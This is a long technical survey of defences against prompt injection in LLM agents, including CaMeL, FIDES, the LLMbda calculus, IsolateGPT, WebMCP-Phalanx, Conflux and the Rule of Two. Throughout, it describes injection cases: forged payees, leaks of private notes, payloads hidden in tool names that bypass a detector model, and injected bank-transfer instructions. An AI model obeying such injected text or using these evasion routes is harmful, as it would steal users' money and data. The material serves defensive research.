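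This avoids exposing the model to any text that an outsider wrote, but anyone who can post messages can still change which channel has the fewest, and therefore which channel Alice ends up in.

| | CaMeL | FIDES |
|---|---|---|
| When the privileged model plans | For the whole task, before any tool runs | Before each action |
| What it sees of tool results | None of their contents | Parts that do not raise the context's label, and names for the rest |
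| How untrusted data can affect later steps | Through branches in the program | Through arguments, or by the model looking at a hidden value |
| What happens after a refusal | The call stops, and the system can ask the user | The model receives a notice and can try another action |

The last option in the third row restricts what the agent may do afterwards, because looking at a hidden untrusted value makes the context untrusted. FIDES has to offer this option for tasks in which the model must read a text before it can choose its next action.

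Other software can check a complete program before it runs. Nikolaou and colleagues built a checker that traces labels through CaMeL's program and looks for forbidden calls. For the bill, it could find the untrusted payee before the agent read any files, then prompt the privileged model for a different program. The checker covers 22 of CaMeL's 28 AgentDojo policies in full. Most of the others depend on facts such as who can currently read a file, so they can't be fully checked until the program runs.

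The checker can also enforce rules about a whole task. For example, it can require an agent that opens a security ticket to eventually close it or pass it on. CaMeL's ordinary policies apply to one call at a time, so they can't express such rules. FIDES never has a complete plan to check, but Costa and colleagues say it could keep a history of past actions and test rules against that.

### Who writes the policies?

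In both systems, a person has to label the sources and specify how serious each tool's actions are, for example that sending money is more serious than reading a calendar. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) argue that this takes expertise most users don't have, and that there is no automatic method for deriving the rules. Users also differ in what they are willing to share, so one expert's policies won't suit everyone.

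Willison, who has worked on application security for two decades, says that any design which requires ordinary users to think about security policies makes him "deeply nervous". He would prefer good defaults and a clear interface. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), which surveyed 13 papers and 14 policy mechanisms in products, gives some reason to share his concern. It found that who writes a policy largely determines how the system enforces it. Developers write code or configuration files, which ordinary software can enforce. End users write plain language, which the model itself has to obey, and an injection may prevent it from doing so.

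Sources can be hard to label correctly. Costa and colleagues suggest that a system can infer an email's readers from its sender and recipients, but this misses anyone who was later forwarded the email. For their tests, they marked a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack targeted it. This is reasonable for a benchmark, but it means they knew where the attacks would be when they assigned the labels. A company that connects an agent to its own mailbox and files doesn't know this in advance, and if it wrongly marks a field as trusted, text injected there gets past every check.

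Even an expert can't write one fixed policy that suits every request. *Sapien* (2026) gives the example of a tool for sending money. An agent needs the tool when a user asks it to issue refunds, but any payment it makes when asked only to summarise the inbox is theft. A fixed policy for a general assistant would have to either block the refunds or allow the theft.

*Sapien* has a language model write a new policy for each task. The model sees only the user's request and the tool descriptions, so text that an attacker plants in an email can't influence the policy. This works the same way as planning before reading untrusted input, but the model can still make mistakes when it writes the policy.

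Those mistakes may be common. *Structured Decomposition for Reliable LLM-Generated Access Control Policies* (2026) tested a model that translated written access rules into code in a single step. The code failed to properly enforce 62.5% of the rules meant to forbid something. In other cases it left out a condition, so that a rule about "the assigned nurse" gave access to every nurse. These were conventional access rules, and the test served as a baseline for a better method, so the results don't carry over directly to agents. They suggest that someone should read a generated policy before relying on it, because incorrect code can still pass a syntax check.

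### Too loose or too strict

If a policy is too loose, the software can approve a harmful call, such as a payment to an attacker, without raising an error. *SPA* (2026) notes that CaMeL is especially exposed to this problem because it has a separate policy for each tool. Separate policies can express finer distinctions than a single rule for all data, but the guarantee depends on every policy being correct and complete. *Only What You've Signed up For* (2026) reports the same dependence in a quite different design, which enforces a policy while the model generates its plan.

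Sometimes a policy lets an attack through because its author didn't count the result as harm. One of AgentDojo's attackers tries to add an event to the user's calendar. The event has no other participants, so it leaks nothing, and Costa and colleagues' policy allows it. Other attacks only change what the agent tells the user, for example by making it praise a hotel. FIDES labels that text as untrusted, and an application could display a warning next to it or refuse to show it. But an application that refused to show any untrusted text couldn't summarise an email.

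A policy that is too strict is at least easy to notice, because the agent stops working. Nikolaou and colleagues ran CaMeL and their checker on AgentDojo's 97 user tasks with no attacker present, and both blocked 17. In tests by Garby and colleagues, CaMeL completed only 37.5% of banking tasks with its policies on. Many of these tasks require the agent to act on a file, which a strict policy is meant to prevent.

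The usual remedy is to ask the user about calls that the policy would block. Labels can reduce the number of questions. Kolluri and colleagues give the example of GitHub's Copilot Chat, which can read without permission but asks before other tool calls. An agent with labels needs to ask only about calls that it cannot show to be within the policy. Instead of asking the user to approve each action that depends on a piece of data, it can also ask them to endorse the data, which is then treated as trusted.

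When an agent asks the user to approve an action, the question has to be specific. Dongol describes an agent in which the user approves a reply to an email, but the software records only that the next message may go out. An injection takes effect before the agent sends the reply, and uses that permission to send private data to the attacker. The software then blocks the user's real reply because the permission has already been used. If the user instead approves the exact recipient and text, the attacker can't substitute a different message.

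For the bill, that means showing the user the account number and the amount. This helps only if the user can recognise the right account number, and someone who asked an agent to pay a bill may never have looked at it. An attack of this kind succeeded against Garby and colleagues' own agent, which can endorse data as part of its plan. The user had asked it to read a file and pay as the file instructed, and the attacker had replaced the contents. This was the only pairing of task and attack that succeeded, in two of 1,296 attacked runs. With endorsement switched off, the agent blocked the attack but could no longer pay genuine bills from a file, because both versions of the file have the same label and no rule about labels can accept one and reject the other.

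## What has been proved about isolation, and under what assumptions?

Researchers can prove that untrusted text has no influence on certain actions, whatever the text contains and however the model reacts to it. A benchmark can't show this because it covers only a limited set of attacks. Such a proof doesn't establish that the text is genuine, since no rule about labels can distinguish a genuine bill from a forged one.

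### Noninterference

Security researchers usually start from a property called noninterference, which Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer defined in 1982. For an agent, keep the trusted input fixed and change the untrusted input in any way. Noninterference holds if this never makes a protected action more or less likely, where a protected action is one that untrusted text should not influence. Write *t* for the trusted input, *u* and *u*′ for any two versions of the untrusted input, and *a* for any protected action. Then:

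Pr(*a* | *t*, *u*) = Pr(*a* | *t*, *u*′)

Suppose a user asks for a summary of an inbox that contains a newsletter. Noninterference requires the agent to be equally likely to delete all the mail whether the newsletter is ordinary or contains an instruction to do so. A model that deletes mail by mistake in 1% of runs still satisfies the property, as long as no newsletter can change that rate.

In the simplest two-model split, the choice of tools satisfies this condition. The privileged model receives the same context in both cases, so the probability that it requests a given tool is the same in both. The same definition works for secrecy if *u* and *u*′ are two versions of the user's private data and *a* is anything an outsider can observe.

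A proof's usefulness depends on which actions it protects. An agent that pays bills from files chooses the payee based on the file, so it violates noninterference if the choice of payee is protected. If only the decision to pay is protected, the agent can satisfy noninterference and still pay the attacker.

The definition uses probabilities because language models usually choose their words partly at random. An agent may send a reminder in one run and not in the next on the same input, so comparing one run on each newsletter would prove little. If the agent sends the reminder in 30% of runs with one newsletter and 35% with the other, the newsletter has some influence on whether the reminder is sent.

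### A leak from code that never runs

Noninterference is defined by comparing two runs of a program, but label-tracking software monitors only one run at a time. If it labels a variable as secret only when an assignment that depends on a secret runs, it can miss leaks like the one in the five-line program from the discussion of CaMeL, which reveals whether a bank balance is high.

| Line of the program | Run with a high balance | Run with a low balance |
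|---|---|---|
| `rich = True` | `rich` is True and public | `rich` is True and public |
| `tmp = True` | `tmp` is True and public | `tmp` is True and public |
| `if balance > threshold: tmp = False` | The assignment runs, so `tmp` becomes False and secret | The program skips the assignment, so `tmp` stays True and public |
| `if tmp: rich = False` | The program skips the assignment, so `rich` stays True and public | The assignment runs, so `rich` becomes False and stays public |
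| `if rich: send_email(...)` | The condition is public, so the email goes out | No email goes out |

The monitor follows its rule correctly in both runs. In the high-balance run, `rich` is True only because the program skipped an assignment, which left the monitor nothing to label. The value of `rich` reveals the balance, but detecting this requires knowing what would have happened in the other run.

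A stricter rule closes the leak by forbidding any change to a public variable when a secret determines whether the change happens. The high-balance run then stops at the third line, where the program tries to change `tmp`. The low-balance run finishes, and neither run sends an email.

Garby and colleagues apply this rule to conversations with a model. One of their test programs first tells the model to remember that *x* is false. If a secret is true, the program sends a second message telling the model to set *x* to true. In either case, it then asks for the value of *x*. When the secret is false, the program skips the second message, so the conversation keeps its public label even though the answer would reveal the secret. Their interpreter prevents this leak by stopping the program if it tries to send the second message.

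### What an unfinished run reveals

Under the stricter rule, the only remaining difference between the two balances is that one run finishes and the other doesn't. Most versions of noninterference don't count this as a leak. A monitor that stops forbidden actions will often stop a run or let it finish depending on the data, so counting every stopped run as a leak would rule out most useful monitors.

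Random models make this exception harder to define. Garby and colleagues first tried comparing the probabilities of outcomes among finished runs only, which turned out to be the wrong definition. The one they settled on is equivalent to the following condition. For each outcome *o* that an observer can see, let *p*(*o*) and *p*′(*o*) be its probabilities under two inputs that should look the same. Each set of probabilities may add up to less than 1, since some runs don't finish. The condition is:

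Σ max(*p*(*o*), *p*′(*o*)) ≤ 1

For example, suppose that with one email an agent sends a summary in 50% of runs, asks the user a question in 30% and stops in 20%. With another email it sends a summary in 40%, asks a question in 40% and stops in 20%. The higher rate for summaries is 50% and the higher rate for questions is 40%. These add up to 90%, so the condition holds, and the stopped runs could account for the whole difference between the two sets of results. If the agent sent a summary in 90% of runs with one email and asked a question in 90% with the other, the higher rates would add up to 180% and the condition would fail.

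The definition also limits how much an observer can learn. The statistical distance between the two sets of outcomes, which is half the sum of the absolute differences in their probabilities, can't exceed the average probability of not finishing. In the first example, the distance is 10 percentage points and the limit is 20. If every run finishes, the limit is zero, so the two sets of probabilities must be equal.

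This limit applies to a single run, so if untracked code outside the monitor keeps restarting a stopped program, an attacker may be able to collect a whole secret one bit at a time.

### What the FIDES guarantee covers

Costa and colleagues chose a weaker property for FIDES, called explicit secrecy. Take any sequence of steps that the agent carries out, and write *g* for its combined effect on the stored data. Two data stores *d*₁ and *d*₂ look the same to an outsider (*d*₁ ≈ *d*₂) if their public parts match. Explicit secrecy requires that:

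if *d*₁ ≈ *d*₂, then *g*(*d*₁) ≈ *g*(*d*₂)

Under explicit secrecy, no sequence of steps may copy a secret into a public place. But the definition takes the steps as given, so it doesn't cover what the agent's choice of steps reveals. If an agent books a specialist only when a confidential test result is positive, the clinic can infer the result from the booking. Explicit secrecy permits this as long as the booking contains nothing copied from the result.

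Costa and colleagues accepted a weaker guarantee than full noninterference, which they considered too restrictive because it would essentially forbid an agent to write anything in a public place after any tool call that might have read a secret. They point out that TaintDroid, which tracked private data on smartphones, made the same compromise. The compromise is sensible for stopping an injection that emails out a document, but poor where a yes-or-no answer is itself sensitive.

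The guarantee covers the FIDES agent loop with any set of tools, but it assumes that the model always gives the same output for the same input. Garby and colleagues credit FIDES with a noninterference theorem in their introduction, but their later discussion of related work describes the guarantee as explicit secrecy, as the FIDES paper does. CaMeL had no comparable theorem, and its developers left a formal treatment to future work.

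### A theorem about every program in a language

Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language, the LLMbda calculus, and proved the probabilistic version of noninterference for every program in it. Its programs can send prompts to a model, receive replies, label data and test labels. They can also run code that the model has written, and the theorem covers that code even if an injection has taken complete control of the model. A program may endorse untrusted values, which weakens the protection against tampering, but a second theorem shows that this can't expose secrets.

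The proof uses an imaginary second interpreter. Whenever a label rises above what a given observer may see, this interpreter skips the computation and returns an empty value. It therefore behaves the same on any two inputs that differ only in data hidden from that observer. It also finishes at least as often as the real interpreter, because it skips steps that could get stuck. So for both inputs, each visible outcome is at least as likely under the imaginary interpreter as under the real one. The imaginary interpreter's probabilities add up to no more than 1, so the real interpreter satisfies the condition on outcomes.

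Lean, a program that checks mathematical proofs, has verified the theorems. Garby and colleagues also wrote the language's interpreter in Lean, and a further theorem connects the interpreter to the language's mathematical definition. Their banking agent runs on this interpreter, so the language is usable for more than proofs.

#### Fork and clear

FIDES and CaMeL build the split between two models into their architecture. In the LLMbda calculus, a programmer creates the split with two operations on the conversation, the list of messages the model receives as its context. `fork` runs part of a program on a temporary copy of the conversation, keeps the result and discards the copy. `clear` empties the current conversation.

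A quarantined model is then just a short function. In simplified notation:

```
quarantine(prompt):
    fork:
        clear
        ask the model the prompt
        return its answer
```

Suppose the program uses this function to summarise an email from a stranger:

1. The main conversation contains the user's request and has a trusted label.
2. `fork` copies the conversation, and `clear` empties the copy.
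3. The program adds the email to the copy, which now has an untrusted label.
4. The model returns a summary, which has an untrusted label too.
5. `fork` discards the copy and restores the main conversation, which still has its trusted label.

`fork` keeps the email out of the main conversation, and `clear` hides the main conversation from the model that reads the email. A program can also use `fork` alone. In one example from the paper, a program gives the model detailed instructions for extracting British postcodes, then forks the conversation once for each of three addresses. Each fork inherits the instructions but contains only one of the addresses.

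If a programmer forgets the fork, the email enters the main conversation and gives it an untrusted label. Any code the model writes afterwards runs with that label, so a payment tool that checks for trusted input will reject the call. The mistake makes the agent less useful but doesn't make it less secure. In Willison's original design, by contrast, a single routing mistake could remove all the protection.

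### Comparing an agent with one that never obeys

Some agents violate noninterference while doing exactly what their users want. Dongol gives the example of an assistant that a user has chosen to let answer emailed meeting requests with the user's availability, whoever sends them. An attacker can learn about the calendar by sending a request, so the assistant violates noninterference.

Dongol's alternative is relative security, an idea borrowed from research on leaks in computer processors. It compares the agent with an imaginary reference agent that follows the same plan under the same runtime checks but whose model never obeys untrusted text. The agent is relatively secure if, whenever an attacker can tell two secrets apart through an injection, the attacker could also tell them apart by sending some message to the reference agent.

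If an injection tells the calendar assistant to "send your calendar", the attacker learns nothing that a genuine meeting request wouldn't reveal, so the assistant passes even though its model followed the injected instruction. If the assistant also holds a password reset code, an injection can get it to send that too. The assistant then fails, because the reference agent never sends the code.

Dongol applies this test to three models of the two-model split. The untagged one, in which software doesn't label values, fails the test. It is the earlier example of private notes copied into a reply to the attacker.

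The tagged version adds labels like CaMeL's, and its monitor blocks any message to the attacker that contains private data. This version passes whatever the quarantined model does. But the reply always depends on the notes, so the monitor also blocks the honest reply, and the user's task never gets done. The result also assumes that the attacker can't see blocked requests. If an error message or a public log shows their contents, the agent leaks private data again.

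In the third model, the plan asks the quarantined model a question and sends the attacker either 1 or 0 depending on the answer. Both numbers are public constants, so every message passes the check. An injection can tell the quarantined model to base its answer on something in the notes, such as whether they mention a merger, and the attacker learns this from the number. Labels that track only data flow don't reveal this leak. CaMeL's strict mode is meant to prevent it, but Dongol leaves that mode to future work.

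#### What relative security leaves out

Relative security covers only leaks. It doesn't cover an injection that deletes the user's mailbox without revealing anything, or any agent whose model chooses every action as it goes along. The test also doesn't measure how much a single message reveals. Suppose the plan lets a stranger guess a PIN once and has the agent reply "yes" or "no", but an injection makes the agent send the whole PIN. The agent still passes, because the stranger could already have told any two PINs apart by guessing one of them. Dongol defines a stricter version that rejects this agent.

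Security results can also depend on what the attacker observes. In an earlier example, the user approved the exact recipient and text of a reply so that an injection couldn't substitute another message. Dongol proves that this is secure against an attacker who sees only the messages and their order. An attacker who also sees when messages arrive can use an injection that tries to send a private value. The monitor allows the call only if the value equals the approved reply, in which case the reply arrives one step early, so the attacker can learn from the timing whether the two match.

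A much simpler defence has a stronger result. When the agent first reads untrusted text, the monitor permanently withdraws every tool that an injection could call. Dongol proves that this makes every plan relatively secure against attackers who see only messages and their order. The theorem assumes that each injection causes a single tool call and that secrets don't affect when the model obeys an injection. The agent also loses the withdrawn tools for legitimate tasks, so it can't reply to an email if reading it removes the mail tool.

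### Checking a plan before it runs

CaMeL's monitor checks only the branch of a program that runs, and it blocks a forbidden call only when the program reaches that call. CaMeLoT, the checker by Nikolaou and colleagues, examines every branch before the agent calls any tool. It translates the program into a finite-state machine, a map of the points the program can reach and the steps between them. Each point records facts such as which tool the program calls there and whether the arguments are trusted. An existing tool called a model checker then searches all the paths for violations.

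The rules use a notation called temporal logic, in which **AG** means "always, on every path" and **AF** means "eventually, on every path". A rule about recipients looks like this in simplified form:

**AG**(send_message → recipient_trusted)

An address that the quarantined model extracted from a message breaks this rule, because CaMeLoT gives that model's answers its lowest level of trust. CaMeLoT describes the offending path in plain language when it asks the privileged model for a new program, and it limits the number of attempts. Since no tool has run yet, the feedback can't contain text from the message.

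A rule can also require steps to happen in a certain order. For example, an agent helping a security team must get approval before disconnecting a computer from the network. If the plan has no approval step, CaMeL would detect this only at the end of what may be a long investigation. CaMeLoT can reject the plan at the start and request one that includes the step.

The checker treats a loop as if it could repeat any number of times, so that it doesn't miss possible violations, but this also makes it reject some safe programs. Its guarantee covers one program and the rules someone has written, whereas the LLMbda theorem covers every program in the language. Rules about who may read a value are still mostly enforced by CaMeL's monitor, so checking the plan first doesn't prevent the bank balance leak.

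### What the proofs take for granted

All the guarantees assume that the user's request is trustworthy, including anything the user has pasted into it. Costa and colleagues also trust the tool descriptions that the privileged model reads. If a company installs a tool from a malicious supplier, the supplier can put an injection in the tool's description, and their FIDES guarantee doesn't cover that attack.

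Labels must be correct where data enters the system. Dongol points out that a calendar is not a trusted source if outsiders can add invitations to it. In the LLMbda calculus, data without an explicit label counts as trusted and public, so a developer who forgets to label a source has in effect marked it safe. The theorem still holds when a label is wrong, but its guarantee then covers the wrong data.

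Policies must also be correct. The LLMbda theorem ensures that labels follow data properly, but labels don't block anything unless each sensitive tool checks them. Garby and colleagues leave those checks to tool developers. CaMeLoT can use a language model to turn the user's request into rules for the task. Ordinary software then rejects rules that name nonexistent tools, but a well-formed rule can still misstate what the user wanted.

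Finally, the software that runs must match the software in the proof. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's interpreter treated an untrusted value as trusted once it was inserted into a piece of text. Their theorems rule out this kind of mistake in their own interpreter, but the proof doesn't cover the code that contacts the model over the network, and it treats tools and data sources as part of the program, not as outside services.

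Dongol lists similar conditions for any deployment. Every tool call and every read of untrusted text must pass through the monitor, and starting a new session must erase everything the model kept from the old one. Showing the user a reply must not have effects the attacker can see, such as loading an image from the attacker's server. Dongol's theorems therefore don't apply to an agent with a browser outside the monitor's control, or with a memory that carries over between sessions.

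## What do separate processes and separate credentials add?

Dongol's theorems hold only if every tool call passes through the monitor. Separating model contexts doesn't ensure this, because one program may call both models, run the tools and store the passwords. An attacker who takes over that program can use the passwords without going through the monitor.

### Two contexts in one program

An operating system runs each program as a process with its own memory, and any code inside a process can usually read all of that memory. Suppose one process calls both models and also holds the access token for the user's calendar. The quarantined model reads a web page and has no tools, so an injection can change only its answer. But before the model receives the page, ordinary code has to download it, decode it and extract the text. If that code has a serious bug, a page built to exploit it can make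 the process run the attacker's own code. That code can then find the token in memory and use it to delete the calendar, even if neither model follows an injected instruction.

*IsolateGPT* (Wu, Roesner and colleagues, 2024) points out that an agent system that runs code for a model may end up running an attacker's code, and that one that keeps its memory in an SQL database may be open to SQL injection.

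Process isolation means running components in separate processes and having the operating system restrict what each can reach. The restrictions are essential because two processes under the same user account can often open the same files. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) recommends controls on files, network connections and processes. It also warns that an agent's harness, the software that connects the model to its tools, doesn't isolate anything by itself.

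The principle for setting those restrictions is least privilege, which means each component gets only the access its job requires. A component that reads web pages needs access to the page, but not to the calendar or the user's documents.

### Keeping the key away from the model

A credential broker is a trusted program that holds a key and uses it on behalf of other components. When the model requests a new calendar event, the broker checks the request, attaches the key, calls the calendar service and returns the result. The key never enters a model's context, so no injection can make a model repeat it.

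OpenAI describes a variant in which a trusted service stores the long-lived credential and issues temporary ones. Each task gets a token tied to the user and the agent, and the agent's software exchanges it for a narrower token that works briefly, for one resource and one action. A thief can do less with such a token than with a password. However, if the service stops issuing tokens, those it has already issued still work until they expire or someone revokes them. Stopping an agent may leave its token valid, and revoking the token may not stop work in progress, so a security team has to do both.

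Hiding a key also doesn't prevent misuse of the access it gives. In one of the guide's examples, an agent that processes invoices notices that a document-signing subscription is about to lapse and tries to renew it. The supplier and the amount may be within the agent's limits, but nobody has authorised the agent to enter a new contract. A broker that checks only the supplier and the amount would make the payment.

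### One request across three processes

Suppose a user asks an assistant to "read this web page and update my calendar", and the page announces a concert. A careful design could use three processes:

- The reader process handles the page and asks the quarantined model about it. It has no keys and no access to the user's files, and it can connect only to the page's website. The controller forwards its requests to the model, so it doesn't need a key for the model service either.
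- The controller runs in its own process. It calls the privileged model, stores values and checks policies.
- The tool process holds the calendar credential and acts as the broker. It accepts only requests to add an event without guests.

The request then goes as follows:

1. The controller passes the user's request to the privileged model, which plans to extract the concert's name, date and time and add them to the calendar.
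2. The reader process downloads the page, extracts the text and has the quarantined model find the three values.
3. The reader sends the values to the controller in a fixed format. The controller rejects an impossible date or an overlong name, and stores the rest as untrusted variables.
4. The privileged model requests a new event, using the variables' names.
5. The controller checks the policy, fills in the values and forwards the request to the tool process.
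6. The tool process checks that the request is for a single event without guests, attaches the credential and calls the calendar service.
7. The controller shows the user the new event.

The table compares an attacker who completely controls the reader, including its code, with one who controls a single process that does everything.

| Attacker's aim | One shared process | Separate reader process |
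|---|---|---|
| Add a false date or a misleading name | Yes | Yes |
| Make the task fail | Yes | Yes |
| Learn what the reader was asked to find | Yes | Yes, if the attacker runs the website |
| Steal the calendar credential | Yes | No, the reader's memory doesn't contain it |
| Read or delete existing events | Yes | No, the tool process only adds events |
| Read the user's documents | Yes | No, the operating system denies access |

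The attacker can also put an injection in the concert's name, where it may affect another agent that reads the calendar next week. Each "No" assumes that the operating system's restrictions work and that the controller handles the reader's messages safely. An attacker who has broken into the reader now needs a second bug to reach the credential.

### IsolateGPT gives each app its own process

Wu and colleagues built IsolateGPT, an early system of this kind, when ChatGPT and similar products had begun to support apps from outside developers. These products put the descriptions of all the apps in one context, so one app's description could give the model instructions about another app. In IsolateGPT, each app has its own process, model instance and memory. A central hub selects the apps a request needs and carries messages between them. The part that carries the messages is ordinary software,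 so it can't follow injected instructions.

An app that needs help from another app must send a request in a format the other app has declared. The hub drops malformed requests and asks the user to approve the rest. Software can check a date or a whole number, but users have to screen free text themselves.

In one test, a user wanted the cheaper of two rides. One app's description contained an instruction to add $10 to the other app's fare. The attack worked in a version of the system without isolation but failed in IsolateGPT, where the malicious app's instructions reached only that app's own model.

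Wu and colleagues also ran 1,598 attacks with GPT-4. In the version without isolation, 20.2% succeeded. In IsolateGPT, 7.6% got as far as a permission dialog, so roughly that share would succeed if the user approved everything. All of those dialogs carried a warning, because the hub had compared the request with a plan it made before any app ran. These were all attacks, so the result doesn't show how often a legitimate request would trigger the same warning. On ordinary tasks, IsolateGPT scored about the same as the version without isolation.

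Each app runs in its own process, but within an app one model may both read untrusted text and use the app's tools. An injection can therefore still take over an email app while it reads a message. Wu and colleagues aim to stop such an attack from spreading, for example to the user's cloud drive, but not to prevent it. Protecting the email app itself would require splitting it into a reader and an actor, as in the calendar example, or relying on the user to check each outgoing message.

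### WebMCP-Phalanx returns approved text

WebMCP is a draft web standard that lets a page offer tools to an agent, such as a shop's checkout function. A shop's page often includes code from advertisers and analytics companies, and the browser gives that code the same rights as the shop's own. An advertiser's script can therefore add its own tools, or remove or replace the shop's.

In one of the two defences in *WebMCP-Phalanx* (Lee, Chang and colleagues, 2026), the browser gives a script an unforgeable credential when the script registers a tool, and only a script with that credential can change or remove the tool. Attacks that removed or replaced tools succeeded in all 20 attempts without this defence and in none with it. The researchers emulated the browser's part in JavaScript, so these results are for a prototype.

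They also split the agent into two models. A quarantined model, which can't call tools, inspects the tools' descriptions and, later, the content the tools return. Text that passes inspection goes to the privileged model, which calls the tools. They tested this arrangement and three weaker ones against injections that tried to make the agent call a malicious tool and send data out.

| Defence | Successful attacks through tool descriptions | Successful attacks through returned content |
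|---|---|---|
| None | 69 of 80 | 42 of 80 |
| Trust labels only | 71 of 80 | 38 of 80 |
| Fixed rules that strip out text | 25 of 80 | 2 of 80 |
| Inspection by the quarantined model | 0 of 80 | 2 of 80 |

These are good results, but the isolation is weaker than in Willison's two-model design, where the privileged model never reads untrusted text and its safety therefore doesn't depend on detecting attacks. In this system, the quarantined model works as a detector, and any injection it misses goes to a model with tools. The quarantined model protects the privileged one only from text it rejects, though Lee and colleagues claim that it absorbs hostile instructions and physically prevents them from steering the privileged model.

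If the browser labels a tool as trusted, the tool's content skips the quarantined model and isn't inspected at all. The label depends partly on whether the tool has a valid credential, but a malicious script can get one as easily as the shop can, so this check doesn't distinguish between them. Both successful attacks in the last row of the table worked because the tool's name suited the task so well that the privileged model called the tool before the inspection was complete.

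The researchers then tested an attacker who knew the quarantined model's instructions and could see whether each attempt worked. This attacker succeeded in 15 of 16 attacks on tool descriptions, usually after one rewrite, by moving the malicious content into the tool's name. Lee and colleagues propose delaying every call until the agent has checked everything it can see about the tool, including the name. This should stop that method, but the privileged model would still read whatever passed the check. A stricter design could show the privileged model only a category from a fixed list, such as "checkout", but the model would then have much less information for choosing between tools.

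Another of their experiments shows why removing a dangerous tool isn't enough. A tool on one page returned an instruction to make a bank transfer, and the agent then moved to another page. The browser removed the tool, but the instruction stayed in the agent's conversation, and the attack's success rate fell only from 80% to 70%. The rate fell to zero when the system also stopped treating the tool's remaining output as trusted.

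### Conflux checks everyone who influenced an action

The tool process in the calendar example can't tell whose text led to a request. Buckley and Schroeder de Witt (2026), in *Conflux*, propose recording this and checking it before each action. They call anyone who can write information for the agent a principal, whether a person or another agent. An action goes ahead only if every principal who influenced it has permission to perform it. For a set *X* of principals:

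allowed(*X*) = {*a* : every *u* in *X* has permission for *a*}

Adding a principal to *X* can remove actions from this set but never add any. The permissions come from the organisation's existing access rules, so nobody needs to write a separate policy for the agent.

Suppose Ava asks an agent to copy a status from Ben's report into a customer record. The agent may do so only if Ava and Ben are both allowed to update that record. If Ben isn't, the software blocks the update, whether or not his report contains an injection.

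The same rule would stop the agent from adding the concert to the user's calendar, even if the details were correct, because the page's author has no permission to change that calendar. Buckley and Schroeder de Witt suggest planning the order of reading and acting to avoid unnecessary refusals. An agent could finish a sensitive action before it opens an outsider's document, or read the document in an isolated branch. Neither helps when the action depends on the document, as adding the concert does.

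The paper proves that the rule prevents any action that an influencing principal isn't allowed to take, provided the records include every influence, which is a hard condition to meet. In the paper's counterexample, an attacker controls a gateway that delivers a trusted colleague's message but holds back another message that conflicts with it. The records name only the colleague, although the attacker has shaped the agent's decision. The rule also doesn't check whether values are true. If Ben may update customer records, he can put a false status in his report.

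The evidence for Conflux is still thin. Buckley and Schroeder de Witt tested different kinds of record on small symbolic cases with no language model involved. The rule allowed all 208 tasks that could be done securely when it had exact records of who had contributed, but wrongly refused 35 of them when the records listed everyone who might have contributed. Their AgentDojo runs only involved reading data, so they don't show whether the rule stops harmful actions. Conflux also doesn't isolate processes, and an attacker who takes over the program that carries out the actions can ignore Conflux's decisions.

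### Which powers may meet in one session?

Few organisations have records as complete as Conflux needs. A simpler precaution is to limit which powers an agent has at the same time. One such limit is to keep an agent from having all three parts of the lethal trifecta (private data, untrusted content and a way to send data out) at once. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) addresses this advice to people who combine tools from different suppliers through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to tools. When researchers report a data theft attack on a product, the supplier can usually close the route by which the data left, but it can't close a new route that a user opens by adding another tool.

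A single tool can also supply all three powers. GitHub's official MCP server could read bug reports from strangers, read private code and publish text in pull requests (proposed changes to code). Willison says CaMeL and the six design patterns can help developers but not users who assemble their own agents. He advises those users to avoid combining the three powers.

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) covers more than data theft. It lists three properties:

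- **A:** the agent processes untrustworthy input.
- **B:** it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** it can change things or communicate with the outside.

An agent may have at most two of these three properties in one session. A session lasts until the agent restarts with a fresh context. If a task requires all three, the agent needs human supervision or some other reliable check. Because property C includes changing things, the rule also covers an injection that makes the agent delete a mailbox.

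Meta applies the rule to an email assistant. Without A, the assistant reads only messages from trusted senders. Without B, it works in a test environment with no real data. Without C, it can write to strangers only after a person has checked the draft. An agent can also change its properties during a session. For example, it can browse the web without access to private data, then permanently lose the ability to communicate before it opens internal systems. It must lose that ability because text from the web is still in its context.

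Separate processes can help an agent follow this rule, depending on what passes between them. In the calendar example, one model reads the page but can't use the calendar, while a second, privileged model requests calendar changes without reading the page. If the controller gave the page's text to the privileged model, that model would have all three properties, even though the first model still ran in its own process.

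In *New prompt injection papers*, Willison, commenting as simonw (2025), objected that Meta's diagram marked the combination of A and C as "safe". He argued that an agent that reads hostile text and can change things may do harm even without access to private data or sensitive systems. One of Meta's examples is a research assistant that fills in web forms, and an injection could make it post spam on other people's websites. Ariel Fogel's report of attacks that need only two of the trifecta's three elements supports this concern.

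Meta's definitions partly address this objection. Property B covers sensitive systems as well as private data, so an agent that can change things only inside a sandbox has little of value to damage. But the research assistant works on the public web and can harm people other than its user. An agent with A and B but not C can also mislead its user with a false summary, which Meta says its rule doesn't prevent.

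Meta presents the rule as a way to avoid the most serious consequences of prompt injection, and doesn't claim that an agent with two of the three properties is safe. It says the rule supplements least privilege, and notes that a design can follow the rule and still fail if the user confirms a warning without thinking. The rule is most useful early in a project, when a developer can still remove one of the properties. The developer then has to work out what an attacker could do with the other two.

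## Can an isolated agent act on what it reads?

The designs described so far work best when an agent can choose its actions before it reads any untrusted text. But users often ask an agent to do things like deal with whatever has arrived in their inbox, and then part of what it reads has to influence what it does next. Designers have tried several ways to limit that influence.

### Tasks that need the data first

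Costa and colleagues call a task data-independent if one fixed sequence of tool calls and one final response would solve it whatever the data turn out to be. Let *D* be all the possible contents of the user's mailbox, files and other stores. For any particular contents *d*, let *S*(*d*) be the set of sequences that solve the task. The task is data-independent if at least one sequence is in every one of these sets:

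⋂ *S*(*d*) ≠ ∅, taken over all *d* in *D*

Any other task is data-dependent.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example request "Send today's schedule to my boss", which is data-independent. The privileged model can write the same two calls, one to read the calendar and one to email the result, whatever the calendar contains.

Costa and colleagues contrast this kind of task with "complete the tasks due today in my TODO app". The agent needs the calendar tool if the list says to book a room, but needs to make a payment if it says to renew a subscription. A privileged model that sees only the name of a hidden variable has the same context in both cases, so it has no basis for choosing between these actions, however capable it is.

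If only the user can edit the list, the software can label it as trusted and let the privileged model read it. Trusting the list becomes a problem when colleagues can add items or the app creates them from incoming email.

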